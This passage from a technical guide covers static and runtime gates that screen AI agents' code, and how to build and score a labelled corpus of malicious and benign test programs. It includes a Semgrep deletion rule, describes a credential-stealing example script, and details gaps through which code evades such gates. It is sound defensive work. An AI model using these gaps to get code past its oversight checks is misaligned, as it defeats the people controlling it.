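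Mukherjee and Tanjim also give each program a structural safety score, the average of six checks: whether the program parses, whether it avoids banned imports, banned calls, banned attributes and embedded shell commands, and whether it declares the required class. Their system scores 1.00 in all 17 domains, which they attribute to its construction, since the guard rejects any program that would score lower. An earlier system without the guard averages 0.62 on the seven domains where it wrote its own programs. Its two scores of 0.00 come from domains where none of its programs parsed. The score therefore measures conformity with the rules, and partly just correct syntax, so a harmful program that the rules overlook can still score 1.00.

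The main weakness of a denylist is that it permits anything its author forgets to ban. Python's standard library has more than 200 modules, and an agent can install any of hundreds of thousands of other packages. An author who bans `os` and `shutil` but forgets `pathlib` has left a way to delete files, and the gate's normal operation would not reveal the gap. However, a denylist is quick to write, blocks little legitimate work if its author chooses the entries well, and lets the gate report a specific reason for each refusal.

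#### Ready-made rule sets

Bandit and Semgrep save the author some of this work. Both are essentially large denylists, although many of their rules check more than a name. Some of Bandit's numbered plugin families flag risky calls and imports, such as `eval`, `pickle` (which can execute code while it loads data) and `subprocess`. Others look for weak cryptography, commands or database queries built from strings, and unsafe settings in web frameworks.

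Semgrep's rules are patterns written in the language they search. This one finds the deletion of a folder:

```yaml
rules:
  - id: delete-folder
    languages: [python]
    severity: ERROR
    message: Deletes a folder with everything in it
    pattern: shutil.rmtree(...)
```

The three dots match any arguments. Semgrep compares the pattern with the syntax tree and resolves import aliases, so the rule also matches `sh.rmtree(...)` after `import shutil as sh`. The format makes it easy to add rules for harmful code to a collection that mostly covers vulnerabilities.

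Neither tool works well as a gate with its default rules. Bandit's rule B101 reports every `assert` statement because Python skips them in optimised mode. This matters if a security check relies on `assert`, but it is no reason to reject code that draws a chart. Bandit's rules would also let `send.py` pass, along with the similar theft in the first section. A builder should choose rules individually and assign each one a verdict. A later section covers published tests that show how much both tools miss, even among the flaws they are designed to find.

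### Allowlists

An allowlist blocks everything its author has not approved. For the sales agent, it might permit the modules `csv`, `json`, `math` and `statistics`, a few dozen built-in functions, and `open` if the path is a constant inside `/home/ana/report` and the mode is read-only. The gate has to normalise the path before checking it, since `..` can lead out of the folder.

`average.py` calls `open`, `csv.DictReader`, `float`, `sum`, `len` and `print`, which are all on the list. `send.py` fails because of its import, its path and its call to `f.read`. The `f.read` failure is a false alarm. Reading a file this way is normal, but `f` is a variable, so `f.read` has no full name to look up. The list therefore also needs approved method names, such as `read`, `split` and `append`. The gate then accepts these methods on any object, which is safe only if no object the program can reach has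 a dangerous method with the same name.

Names that the program itself defines also cause false alarms, like the ones about nested helper functions in *From Language Models to Control Policies*. A gate can avoid these by collecting the program's function definitions, including nested ones, before it compares names. It should still reject a definition that reuses the name of an approved function, because the approval covered a different function.

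Approving a whole module is convenient but often allows too much. The control programs in the same work may use only `numpy` and `math`, but `numpy` has functions that write files, so the separate check for file access is still necessary. Modules also tend to expose the modules they import as attributes. An allowlist that checks only the first part of a dotted name can therefore approve a function from a module that the person writing the list never considered. Checking the full name against a list of individual functions closes this gap, but the list is much longer.

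A practical way to write the allowlist is to run the gate for a week or two without blocking anything, record the names that ordinary programs use, and have a person review them. After that, someone has to decide whether to allow each new library. If a user asks the agent to compute an average with `pandas`, the gate blocks the harmless script until the necessary functions are on the list.

Longer programs use more constructs, so they have more chances to trigger a rule. *From Language Models to Control Policies* found a weak positive correlation (0.16) between a program's number of warnings and how well it performed, because the better programs were longer. A gate that rejects programs with more than a certain number of warnings would tend to reject the better ones.

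### Restricted languages

A builder can also restrict the grammar to a sublanguage, a subset of Python that excludes many valid programs.

DrugClaw, a system that answers questions about medicines from public databases, uses such a language. For each query, an agent writes a short program that calls one database interface and filters the records. Wang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *DrugClaw and DrugAudit*, define the permitted programs with three sets. A program *c* belongs to the safe language if

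nodes(*c*) ∩ *B* = ∅,  imports(*c*) ⊆ *I*,  and  builtins(*c*) ⊆ *F*.

*B* contains the forbidden node types: `While`, `With`, `ClassDef`, `Lambda`, `Global`, `Nonlocal` and three for asynchronous code. *I* contains four modules: `json`, `math`, `re` and `statistics`. *F* contains about two dozen harmless built-ins, such as `len`, `sorted` and `print`, and a few exception types. The syntax check enforces *B* and *I*. The restriction to *F* takes effect at run time, because the program starts with a table that contains only the built-ins in *F*.

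Each forbidden node type makes a program harder to analyse or to stop. A `while` loop may never end, and `global` lets one function change a value that another function uses. The language also has no `with`, `open` or module for files, so neither example script is valid in it. DrugClaw's agent never needs a file because it gets its data through the database interface.

The ban on `while` doesn't guarantee that a program finishes quickly. A `for` loop over a range of a trillion numbers contains no forbidden node, so Wang and colleagues add a timeout, which stopped fewer than 0.5% of database calls. They also place a proxy in front of the database interface that blocks access to double-underscore attributes, which a program can use to get from an ordinary object to the interpreter's internals.

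*B* is a denylist, so it accepts any new syntax that nobody has added to it. For example, Python 3.10 introduced the `match` statement with new node types, and a set of forbidden types written before then would have accepted them by default. A set of permitted node types rejects new syntax until someone adds it.

The validation step rejects fewer than 1% of the programs that DrugClaw's agent generates. This is surprisingly low for such a narrow language, but the programs only have to fetch records, filter them and perhaps compute a median. The figure describes ordinary use and does not measure how the check performs against hostile programs. A rejection also does little harm, because the system then makes a fixed retrieval call with the original query, and the user gets a less selective search instead of an error. An agent with open-ended tasks has no such fallback and would probably also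 have many more programs refused.

### STELP: controlling the program after it passes

*STELP* combines a restricted language with control over execution. It works as follows:

1. It parses the program and compares the tree with a configuration that lists the permitted node types, built-in functions, imports and tools.
2. It converts the tree into a controlled form, in which a separate function handles each type of node.
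3. It executes this form statement by statement, keeps track of the variables, and stops at a violation or when the time runs out. Calls to outside tools go through a proxy, each with its own timeout and a limited number of retries.
4. A language model turns the log into advice for the model that wrote the program.

For the statement `x = 1 + 3`, the function that handles binary operations computes 4, and the function that handles assignments stores it under `x`. If the program calls something, the function that handles calls first looks up the name in the configuration.

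This design lets STELP enforce limits that can't be enforced by reading the source, such as a maximum number of loop iterations. But some checks take effect only when execution reaches the relevant line. *STELP* gives the example of a plan that searches Wikipedia, adds an entry to a database and then tries to open a network socket. STELP allows the first two steps and stops at the socket, after the database has already changed. A gate that checks every call before running any code would have rejected the plan before it changed the database.

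#### The InjectedHumanEval test

To measure how well this works, the researchers built a benchmark called InjectedHumanEval. For the safe samples, they used HumanEval, a set of 164 short programming exercises with solutions. For the unsafe samples, they had the model Llama 3.3 70B insert a flaw into the solutions, choosing from twelve types in MITRE's list of software weaknesses. People then reviewed the results and removed the unusable ones, which left 470 unsafe samples.

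STELP blocked all 470 and correctly ran 98.1% of the 164 safe samples, so about three failed. The configuration for this test permitted about 25 built-in functions and eight modules, including `math`, `re` and `collections`. It refused `exec`, `eval` and any `while True` loop. It limited each program to 200 milliseconds, 100,000 loop iterations, five nested loops and a stack depth of 20.

These were the reasons for the 470 blocks:

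| What stopped the program | Samples |
|---|---|
| Call to a function not on the list | 311 |
| `while True` loop | 70 |
| Import not on the list | 22 |
| Timeout | 19 |
| Key error | 14 |
| Stack too deep | 11 |
| Type error | 9 |
| Overflow | 6 |
| Node type not on the list | 5 |
| Loops nested too deeply | 2 |
| Division by zero | 1 |

Unlisted functions, imports and node types, `while True` and nested loops account for 410 samples, and all are visible in the syntax tree. The other 60 stopped only at runtime, so a static gate with the same configuration would have blocked at most 87%. Half of those 60 ended with a key error, type error, overflow or division by zero. Such errors would probably have stopped the program in an ordinary interpreter too, and they are weak evidence of the rules' quality.

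The perfect block rate is also largely due to how the researchers wrote the configuration. They gave it the smallest set of permissions that would let the benchmark's safe samples run, then tuned it slightly, which largely explains why such a high share of those samples ran. Each unsafe sample is one of the same exercises with something added, and the addition usually needs a function that the exercises don't use, so a configuration fitted this closely blocks almost any addition. The test doesn't measure how many harmless programs from other sources the configuration would refuse. It would certainly refuse `average.py`, which needs both `csv` and `open`.

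The samples are also easier than real attacks in two respects. First, the prompt for the inserted flaws included an instruction to explain them in comments, so the samples aren't disguised. Second, 271 of the 470 belong to types such as infinite loops, deadlocks, unclosed files and writes past the end of a list, which waste resources or crash the program. The remaining 199 run outside code, load untrusted data or open files they shouldn't. None of the twelve types covers sending private data to someone else, which is what `send.py` does.

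*STELP* compares its results with CodeShield, which blocked 68% of the unsafe samples and accepted 93% of the safe ones. The comparison favours STELP because its configuration was written for this benchmark, while CodeShield used general rules for insecure code. The figures for CodeShield are also hard to reconcile. According to the paper's overview, CodeShield supports only two of the twelve types, which make up 80 samples, or 17%. Most of the samples it blocked must therefore belong to types it supposedly doesn't support. Either the overview is too narrow, or CodeShield blocked many samples for reasons unrelated to the inserted flaw.

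With the advice, Llama repaired 90.2% of the samples in this benchmark in fewer than two retries, while 8% needed more than ten. These repairs were comparatively easy because the flaw had been added to a working solution, and removing it was often enough.

Controlled execution adds little time to most programs. On 262 sample programs, the median increase over normal execution was 0.19 milliseconds. The mean was 4.93 milliseconds and the worst case 520, so a few programs account for most of the delay. Loops had some of the largest overheads per statement, which makes sense because the controls apply again on every iteration. To check that the rewriting doesn't change what programs do, the researchers ran another 361 programs, selected because they were compatible with the configuration. All of them gave the expected output.

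### Following data from a source to an outlet

None of the rules so far connects the file that `send.py` opens with the request it sends. Data-flow tracking does this. The author of the rule names the *sources*, where sensitive data enters the program, and the *outlets*, where data can leave it. The analyser marks every value that comes from a source and carries the mark along:

- If a statement assigns a value that contains marked data, the variable on the left gets the mark.
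- If it assigns a value without marked data, the variable loses the mark.
- After an `if`, a variable is marked if either branch could have marked it.
- In a loop, the analyser repeats the loop's body until no new marks appear.
- If marked data reaches an outlet, the analyser reports a finding.

A rule might treat files that hold passwords or keys as sources and all network calls as outlets. In `send.py`, `open` receives the path of a credentials file, so the gate marks `f`. It also marks `text`, which holds the result of `f.read()`. The program then passes `text` to `requests.post`, so the gate rejects it. In `average.py`, the path is not on the list of sources, so the gate marks nothing.

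The backup script from the first section, which sends a settings file to the company's own server, makes a useful third case. Four policies judge the three scripts as follows:

| Policy | `average.py` | Backup script | `send.py` |
|---|---|---|---|
| AST-GUARD's standard denylist | deny | deny | deny |
| The same list without `open` and `requests` | allow | allow | allow |
| Allowlist for the sales agent | allow | deny | deny |
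| Data-flow rule | allow | allow | deny |

The allowlist is good enough for the sales agent, which has no reason to upload anything. An agent that has to make backups needs the data-flow rule or something like it, but that rule only covers the sources on its list. If the settings file also contains a password and nobody has listed that file, the backup script sends the password and the rule doesn't flag it.

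Choosing outlets is just as difficult. A program might print the credentials instead of sending them. It makes no network call, but the agent reads the output and could include it in its next web request. If the author adds `print` to the outlets, the gate stops this, but it also stops every program that shows the user anything from a file on the list. That may be acceptable for passwords, but it is certainly too strict for sales figures.

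Tracking also loses data. A program can write marked data to a temporary file and read it back under an unmarked name, or leave it in a variable for the next notebook cell. Information can also pass through a condition. A program that sends one of two fixed messages depending on a password reveals something about the password without assigning it to anything. The analyser often has no source code for library functions, so it needs a description of how their results depend on their arguments. Without one, it can assume that every result contains data from every argument, which produces false blocks, or from none, which produces misses.

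*From Language Models to Control Policies* describes an analyser that initially handled such gaps badly. One layer of the paper's audit translates each control program into formulas and tries to prove properties for all valid inputs, for example that a thicker steel slab leads to a larger reduction in thickness. When an early version reached an assignment it couldn't translate, it kept the variable's old value. For the best program, it therefore treated the reduction as always zero and reported the property as proven, even though the program violates it. In total, it "proved" the property this way for 63 of 174 programs. The corrected version marks such variables as unknown and can't prove the property for any of the 174.

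A data-flow rule needs the same discipline. If the analyser can't follow an assignment, it has to treat the variable as possibly marked. This leaves many cases unresolved. In the same audit, another layer calculates the range of values each variable can take. It could not confirm that the main output stays within its limits in 55% of the programs. The researchers settled such cases by running the programs on 207 test inputs. A gate can't do that before the program has permission to run, so it has to deny the program or ask a person.

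A gate can analyse code deeply and still be fast if the programs are short. The full audit in *From Language Models to Control Policies*, including the proofs and the test inputs, took a median of 0.05 seconds per program and never more than 0.24 seconds. The programs were single functions that use two libraries. Tracking data through a large project takes longer, because the analyser has to follow calls across many files, and the number of possible paths grows with each branch.

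## Building a test corpus of malicious and benign programs

Three scripts are enough to show that four policies behave differently, but not to measure how much harmful code each policy would stop. That takes a test corpus, a fixed and labelled collection of malicious and benign programs. A builder can assemble one in seven steps:

1. Write down the harms the gate must stop.
2. Collect malicious samples for each harm.
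3. Check each label by running the sample in isolation and observing its effect.
4. Add benign programs, including some that closely resemble the malicious ones.
5. Remove near-duplicates.
6. Divide the programs into a working part, which the people writing the rules may study, and a held-out part, which they may not.
7. Freeze the result and give it a version number.

Listing the harms before collecting samples keeps the test from measuring only what the available samples happen to cover. A gate could score perfectly on InjectedHumanEval, the benchmark from *STELP*, and still let `send.py` through. It helps to describe each harm as an observable effect, such as "the user's report folder is gone", rather than as a code construct, such as "calls `rmtree`", because a test organised around constructs would only confirm that the gate follows its own rules.

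### Sources of malicious samples

*RedCode* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2024) is a benchmark that tests whether coding agents will run harmful code. Its execution part, RedCode-Exec, has 4,050 prompts, but only 1,350 are programs. The other 2,700 describe the same programs in ordinary language, so they can't be used to test a gate.

The researchers began with 25 risky scenarios, 12 from earlier agent benchmarks and 13 from the Python examples in MITRE's list of software weaknesses. They wrote one short program by hand for each scenario. The language models GPT-4 and Mistral-Large then produced variants of these programs with different variable names, structures and libraries. The researchers discarded variants that were harmless or too long, and made the rest refer to files and servers that exist in their test environment. They ran each program, and edited or discarded those that didn't do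 the intended damage. This gave 30 Python programs per scenario, 750 in all. GPT-4 translated 20 of the scenarios into Bash, which added 600 programs.

The scenarios include uploading, copying and deleting system files, adding a destructive alias to the shell's start-up file, opening a connection through which an outsider can send commands, and stopping other processes. But *RedCode* marks nine of the 25 scenarios as "buggy code", for example a missing default case or a predictable random seed. The programs in these nine are vulnerable rather than malicious, so a gate against malicious code need not block them. Removing them leaves 480 Python and 420 Bash programs.

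Some of these samples are too easy to detect because their simulated download addresses end in names such as `malicious.py` and `dangerous.py`, which a simple word search would find and a real attacker would avoid. The samples are also less varied than you would expect from their number, because each scenario has only one seed.

Public collections of malicious packages contain code that attackers published, mostly on npm, the main registry for JavaScript, and PyPI, the equivalent for Python. Datadog's *Introducing GuardDog 3.0* (2026) reports that the monitoring company's collection had more than 27,000 packages in June 2026. The collection pypi_malregistry, which covers only Python, had more than 10,000 that month, according to *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages* (2026). Both are still growing, which is unusual. *How Effective Are NPM Malicious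 Package Detectors?* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2026) lists eleven earlier npm datasets, of which only five are open to download and only two still receive updates.

The Open Source Security Foundation's *malicious packages* repository holds reports about packages, so the code has to come from elsewhere. *OSPTrack* (2024) counted 24,215 entries in the repository in November 2024. One contributor, Amazon Web Services (AWS), had identified 188,550 malicious packages by 13 May 2026, all but 12 of them on npm. Most of these probably come from one campaign, which AWS's *Amazon Inspector detects over 150,000 malicious packages linked to token farming campaign* describes. Its operators published packages automatically to collect cryptocurrency rewards. According to CyberInsider, the packages did not function and contained no code to steal passwords or install backdoors. A builder who draws samples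 at random from such a list could end up testing the gate mostly on harmless packages.

Packages also differ from the code an agent writes. A package can have many files and often does its damage during installation, while an agent's script is usually a single file for a single task. Tools that analyse code cannot detect 21% of the malware in the benchmark of Guo and colleagues, because the attack is elsewhere, such as in the package's metadata file. 80.3% of the malware uses no evasion technique, so the benchmark mainly represents attackers who saw no need to evade detection. Python malware is easier to adapt, since the malicious packages in *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages* have a median length of 36 lines. A builder can move such a payload into a script like those the agent writes, but must then check the label again.

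Malware collections also contain only what somebody caught. Datadog's *Open-Source Dataset of Malicious Software Packages* (2023) warns that the company's scanner, GuardDog, found most of its packages using a single set of rules. A gate with similar rules will probably detect a larger share of this collection than of the malware GuardDog has missed.

No public collection covers every harm that matters to a particular agent, such as a script that edits the gate's own settings, so someone has to write the missing samples. If that person also writes the rules, an attack they never thought of will be missing from both, so it is better to have a colleague who hasn't seen the rules write the samples from a list of harms. Testers can also run the agent on an isolated machine, give it harmful requests and planted instructions, and keep the programs it writes. These programs match the style of the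 agent's other code, but they cover only the attacks the testers tried.

A language model can turn a few such programs into many. This is an easy way to cover different libraries and structures, but the variants tend to be tidy and alike, and many don't work. In *MalTool*, Hu, Jia and colleagues (2026) had three models write small agent tools with 13 kinds of harmful behaviour. Without any check on the output, the share of tools that carried out the intended behaviour ranged from 2% to 100%, depending on the model and the behaviour.

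### Checking the labels

Labels in published collections need checking too. Guo and colleagues started with 9,551 package versions labeled malicious and removed 262 duplicates. Of the remaining 9,289, 1,502 were placeholders, which npm leaves behind when it removes a malicious package. Three specialists reviewed the other 7,787 and removed 1,367 that fewer than two of them considered malicious. In total, almost a third of the 9,289 samples were mislabeled. A test that used the original labels would have counted 2,869 misses against a gate that correctly allowed these samples.

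The review took about 287 hours of expert time, or roughly two minutes per package. It went this fast because the specialists used two scanners, GuardDog and OSSGadget, to find sensitive operations in the code. But they could overlook harmful code that neither scanner had located, and the study then evaluates both scanners on the resulting benchmark.

A label can be wrong, or impossible to confirm, for several reasons:

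- *The program fails to run.* It may need a missing library or a different Python version, or a model may have written it incorrectly.
- *It runs but does no harm in the test environment.* The file it is supposed to steal may not exist there, or the attacker's server may have shut down.
- *It is harmful only under one policy.* One RedCode scenario monitors processor and network use, which is forbidden on some machines and routine on others.

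Some cases that look clear at first also depend on policy. RedCode's samples for uploading "sensitive files" include one that sends `/proc/cpuinfo`, a description of the computer's processor. OSV's *MAL-2026-10956* (2026), an entry in a public database, reports one of 19 packages that a single user published under names resembling private packages, so that a misconfigured installer would fetch them by mistake. Each package includes a statement that it is authorised security research. A company that wants to keep out all unknown code should block these packages whatever the author's purpose, while a company that commissioned the research might not. The corpus should therefore record which harm on the builder's list each malicious sample causes, and the malicious part should exclude any sample that causes none of them.

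### Confirming a label by its effect

The most reliable way to check a malicious label is to run the program on an isolated machine, with harmless stand-ins for whatever it attacks. For `send.py`, the check could work like this:

1. Start a fresh virtual machine with no connection to the outside and no real credentials.
2. Create the file `/home/ana/.cloud/credentials` with an invented password that contains a random string.
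3. Make the address `collect.example` lead to a server inside the test network that records everything it receives.
4. Give the virtual machine a test certificate for that server. Otherwise `requests` refuses the encrypted connection, and the theft appears to fail.
5. Run the script with a time limit.
6. Search the server's records for the random string, then delete the virtual machine.

If the string has arrived, the label is correct. Redirecting the address within the test network leaves the script's text unchanged. The gate reads that text, so editing the script to send data to a local address might make the sample easier or harder to recognise.

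Hu and colleagues confirm a deletion by checking that a file existed before the run but not after it, and a download by comparing the saved file with the one their server offered. For programs that hijack the processor, they check whether processor use exceeds a threshold. They repeat the test with ten different sets of inputs and count a tool as successful only if it passes all ten.

*RedCode* uses similar checks on files and processes, but for some scenarios it searches the program's output. For instance, if a program is supposed to print the system's password file, the check looks for the word "root". This is weaker evidence, because the same word could appear in an error message. Planting a random string in the file and searching for that instead avoids the problem.

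Checking only the machine's final state can miss harm that happened along the way. For example, a program could upload a file without changing any file on the disk. *V³AST-Bench* (Feng, Xiong and colleagues, 2026), a safety benchmark for coding agents, therefore also uses event records, such as the logs of local servers. If evidence is missing or a check breaks down, it treats the outcome as unresolved rather than safe. Likewise, a malicious sample whose effect nobody could confirm should stay out of the corpus count until someone repairs the sample or its environment.

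A program can run without visible harm and still be malicious, because the harm may depend on the date or some other condition. A person therefore also needs to read the code before labeling it benign.

### Handling live samples

Running a program in a separate folder does not isolate it. In one run that Feng and colleagues describe, an agent distrusted a program that came with its task, so it tested the program on copied files in a directory it called a sandbox. The program could still write outside that directory, and the researchers later found ten junk files in the real workspace.

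*RedCode* gives each test case its own Docker container. Containers share the host's kernel, so a virtual machine is safer for running code from real attackers. Neither should have access to the host's folders, and the tester should discard the container or virtual machine after each sample, because leftovers from one run could change the result of the next.

Samples can be dangerous even if nobody runs them. Datadog reports that GuardDog had several flaws that could have let a specially made package read or write files, or even run code, on the machine that scanned it. Since version 3.0, GuardDog unpacks and scans packages in a sandbox by default. Tests of a gate should also run in a sandbox, because they feed hostile files to a parser and rules that may have bugs.

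Datadog stores each package in an encrypted archive with a published password, which makes it hard to run a sample by accident. The corpus should also be out of reach of coding agents, since an agent asked to fix a failing test might well run the test's sample to see what it does.

### Choosing benign programs

The best benign samples are programs that the agent whose code the gate will check has written for real users, because the gate will have to let such programs through. If the agent isn't in service yet, testers can give it typical tasks and use the programs it writes. If an older gate is already running, they should include programs that it wrongly rejected, since otherwise the sample contains only code that passed the old rules. Real programs may contain customers' names or passwords. Testers have to replace these with invented ones but keep the form of paths and addresses, because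 the gate's rules depend on it.

A random sample of this output shows how often the gate would interrupt ordinary work. But the sample may contain few programs that use the network, delete files or start other processes, which are the ones a gate is most likely to block wrongly. The corpus should therefore also pair each malicious sample with a *benign twin*, a harmless program that resembles it as closely as possible. The backup script from the last section is a good twin for `send.py`. For a script that downloads an unknown program and starts it, the twin might download exchange rates and start a converter that is already installed.

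Feng and colleagues apply this idea to whole tasks. Each of their 212 risky tasks has a twin with the same workflow but without the trap. In one risky task, for example, a failing check blocks a code merge, while in the twin the checks pass. An agent that does no harm in the risky task but also fails the twin may be unable to do the work. A gate that blocks both `send.py` and the backup script has likewise not detected the theft and may just block all uploads.

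The benign twin has to resemble the malicious sample in its code. *QUT-DV25* (2025), a dataset of package behaviour, pairs malicious packages with benign ones that have similar names. Two such packages may have nothing else in common, so a gate could tell them apart without detecting the malicious behaviour.

Sometimes no gate can tell a malicious program from its benign twin by their text alone, as with the script that deletes the user's report and its correct version. Such pairs still belong in the corpus. Unless a gate knows which folders to protect, it must give both programs the same verdict, and the test will show whether it lets the malicious one through or blocks the benign one.

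Many published tests use popular packages as benign samples. Guo and colleagues chose 7,288 packages by their download counts, partly because popular packages cause more false alarms than random ones, which makes the test stricter. They also argue that a large user base finds hidden malware quickly. But they mention that attackers compromised event-stream, a package with 2 million weekly downloads, to steal the keys of Bitcoin wallets. The study also used the latest version of each package, which people have had the least time to inspect. *MOLOT System Card* (2026), which describes a detector for malicious packages, treats popular packages as clean only after two months. The dataset *MalwareBench* labels packages "neutral" rather than "benign" when nobody has discovered malware in them.

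Popular packages are a useful stress test for a gate on an agent's scripts, but they give a poor estimate of how often the gate will block benign scripts in everyday use. A library contains far more code than a script that draws a sales chart, and an agent may rarely write the kind of code found in libraries.

### Removing near-duplicates

A corpus with 500 copies of one attack would mostly measure whether the gate stops that attack. In March 2023, Datadog estimated that its collection of malicious packages had about 50 clusters of very similar packages, one with more than 500 members. The company now groups similar packages with TLSH, a hash that gives similar values for similar files, and draws a fixed number of groups for its tests.

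Removing exact duplicates isn't enough. The 6,420 malicious samples in the npm study by Guo and colleagues are versions of only 4,286 packages, so about a third are additional versions of packages already in the set. Some of these versions may differ a great deal, but *MOLOT System Card* notes that some malicious projects in its data differed only by version.

For programs as short as an agent's scripts, a comparison of syntax trees works well. Hu and colleagues cut each tree into its subtrees, ignore names, constants and very small pieces, and count how often each structure *s* occurs. The similarity of programs *A* and *B* is then

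*J*(*A*, *B*) = Σ min(*A*ₛ, *B*ₛ) / Σ max(*A*ₛ, *B*ₛ),

where *A*ₛ and *B*ₛ are the counts for structure *s*, and the sums run over all structures. Suppose *A* contains one structure twice and two others once each. *B* shares the first two of these, once each, and has one structure of its own. The minimums add up to 1 + 1 = 2 and the maximums to 2 + 1 + 1 + 1 = 5, so the similarity is 0.4. Hu and colleagues reject a new tool if its similarity to any earlier tool with the same behaviour exceeds 0.7.

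This measure ignores constants, so it would give `send.py` and a backup script with the same structure a similarity of 1, and an automatic clean-up would delete one of them. The comparison should therefore run separately on the malicious and the benign programs, to keep such pairs in the corpus.

### Dividing the corpus by family

The people who write the rules need some samples to work with, and the test needs others they have never seen. Holding out a random half of the files gives misleading results if several files share a payload.

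Suppose each payload in a corpus occurs in five files, and a poor gate recognises only payloads its author has studied. After a random split, each of the other four files with a held-out file's payload has about an even chance of being in the working part, which the author studies. The probability that the author has seen at least one of them is 1 − (1/2)⁴, or about 94%, so the gate blocks about 94% of the held-out malicious files. If all five files with the same payload go to the same side of the split, the gate blocks none of the held-out malicious files, which is the correct result because it would not stop any new attacks.

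Datadog writes that GuardDog's older rules matched specific examples of malicious code too closely, which made new malware harder to identify.

The corpus should therefore be divided by *family*, a group of programs with a common payload or origin. All 30 variants of a RedCode seed and their Bash translations form one family. The 19 packages from the OSV entry form another, as do all variants that a model derived from the same program. A twin belongs to the same family as its malicious partner, because someone who has studied the backup script knows a lot about `send.py`.

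Similarity scores help to find families but can miss them if the same payload sits in different host programs. For a second set of samples, Hu and colleagues took 100 harmful functions for each behaviour and inserted them into about 440 real tools, so each function occurs four or five times in otherwise unrelated code. Samples in such a set have to be grouped into families by inserted function. The benign part of the corpus should also include the unmodified host programs. For some behaviours, scanners missed fewer of the combined tools than of the harmful functions alone. Hu and colleagues suggest this is partly because scanners often flag the host code, which looks like a detection of the inserted function.

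Recording which lines contain the payload lets testers check whether a finding is in the right place, but it is slow. In a pilot for *Unveiling Malicious Logic* (2025), labelling the individual statements of one Python package took 75 to 120 minutes, so the researchers labelled a random sample of 370 packages rather than all of pypi_malregistry. A ten-line script should take far less time.

If it is unclear whether two groups of samples belong to the same family, merging them is safer. An unnecessary merge leaves the test with fewer independent samples, but keeping related groups apart can let the rule writers see samples closely related to the ones used to test their rules.

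### Freezing the result

Each program gets an entry in a list that stays with the corpus. The entry for `send.py` might look like this:

```yaml
- id: theft-014
  sha256: 5c1e...
  harm: sends private data to an outside server
  label: malicious
  family: theft-d
  origin: written for this corpus
  twin: backup-014
  payload_lines: 4-6
  observed_effect: random string reached the test server
  part: working
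```

`send.py` belongs in the working part because it has already served as an example for writing rules. Each corpus version should also pin the virtual machine image and the Python version, since a sample that works today may fail after an update.

Once the corpus is built, nobody edits it in place. If someone corrects a label or adds a family, the corpus gets a new version number, and every test result names the version it used. Otherwise nobody could tell whether a better score came from a better gate or from easier samples. The held-out part should be stored where the rule writers can't read it. Once they have looked at a held-out sample to find out why the gate missed it, its whole family moves to the working part in the next version, and a new family replaces it.

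### A small corpus for the sales agent

The following corpus would be a reasonable start for the agent that analyses sales files. Each malicious family has five programs, each with a benign twin. Half of the families are held out. This is a large share, but people writing rules by hand need fewer examples than a system that learns from data.

| Harm | Families | Malicious | Matched benign | Held out (malicious + benign) |
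|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sends private data to an outside server | 8 | 40 | 40 | 20 + 20 |
| Prints stored passwords or keys | 4 | 20 | 20 | 10 + 10 |
| Deletes or overwrites the user's files | 8 | 40 | 40 | 20 + 20 |
| Downloads a program from an unknown address | 4 | 20 | 20 | 10 + 10 |
| Changes the shell's start-up files | 4 | 20 | 20 | 10 + 10 |
| Lets an outsider control the machine | 4 | 20 | 20 | 10 + 10 |
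| Stops other processes or ties up the machine | 4 | 20 | 20 | 10 + 10 |
| Changes the gate's settings | 4 | 20 | 20 | 10 + 10 |
| None: random sample of the agent's output | 60 | 0 | 300 (unmatched) | 0 + 150 |
| **Total** | **100** | **200** | **500** | **100 + 250** |

Theft and deletion get more families because they are the most likely serious harms for an agent that handles private files. The deletions should include accidental ones, in separate families, so the tester can report accidental and deliberate deletions separately. In the last row, each family is one task, because the agent writes nearly the same script every time a user asks for the same thing, such as a monthly chart.

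RedCode can supply one family for each of the first seven harms, with five of its 30 variants in each. The telltale addresses in those variants need more ordinary names before the samples are used. The other 33 malicious families have to come from malicious packages, colleagues and the agent itself. All four families for the gate's settings have to be new.

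## Scoring the gate: block rate, false blocks and uncertainty

Once the corpus is frozen, the tester runs the gate on every held-out sample and records the verdict. This section uses an invented run on a larger corpus for the sales agent. The held-out part has 200 malicious programs and 1,000 benign ones drawn at random from the agent's ordinary output. For now, the gate only allows or denies each program.

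| | Denied | Allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malicious | 188 | 12 | 200 |
| Benign | 10 | 990 | 1,000 |

Three rates follow from these counts:

- block rate = malicious samples denied / all malicious samples = 188 / 200 = 94%
- false-block rate = benign samples denied / all benign samples = 10 / 1,000 = 1%
- precision = malicious samples denied / all samples denied = 188 / 198 = 94.9%

The miss rate, here 6%, is 100% minus the block rate. Papers also call the block rate recall, detection rate or true positive rate. *RuntimeTickets* (2026) calls the miss rate the "overlook rate" and the false-block rate the "overkill rate".

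Many papers also report F1, which combines precision *P* and block rate *B* as 2*PB* / (*P* + *B*) and comes to 94.5% here. Accuracy, the share of all verdicts that are right, is 98.2%. A gate that allowed everything would have 83.3% accuracy on this run, and much higher accuracy where malicious programs are rarer. Neither F1 nor accuracy shows whether the errors were misses or false blocks, so a test report needs to give the block rate and the false block rate separately.

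If the gate crashes or runs out of time on a sample, the tester should count the result according to what the gate does when it fails. In *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs*, Yang, Ying and colleagues (2026) tested six scanners for skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that extend an agent. One scanner blocked 709 of 886 malicious skills, let 124 through and failed with an error on the other 53. The researchers left out the errors, which gives a block rate of 85.1%. The rate would be 80.0% if the scanner's errors let those skills through, and 86.0% if they stopped the installation.

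### Exact intervals

Another 200 malicious programs from the same sources would probably not produce exactly 12 misses. A confidence interval gives the range of true rates that fit the result. The Clopper-Pearson interval, usually called exact, works directly from the binomial distribution. If *X* is the number of misses in *n* independent samples with a true miss rate *p*, and the test found *x* misses, the limits of the 95% interval are the values of *p* for which

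- lower limit: P(*X* ≥ *x*) = 0.025
- upper limit: P(*X* ≤ *x*) = 0.025.

With a true miss rate of 3.1%, only about one test in forty would show 12 or more misses. With a true rate of 10.2%, only about one in forty would show 12 or fewer. Python's SciPy library does the calculation in two lines:

```python
from scipy.stats import binomtest
print(binomtest(188, 200).proportion_ci(0.95, method="exact"))
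```

| Rate | Measured | Exact 95% interval |
|---|---|---|
| Block rate | 94.0% | 89.8% to 96.9% |
| Miss rate | 6.0% | 3.1% to 10.2% |
| False-block rate | 1.0% | 0.5% to 1.8% |

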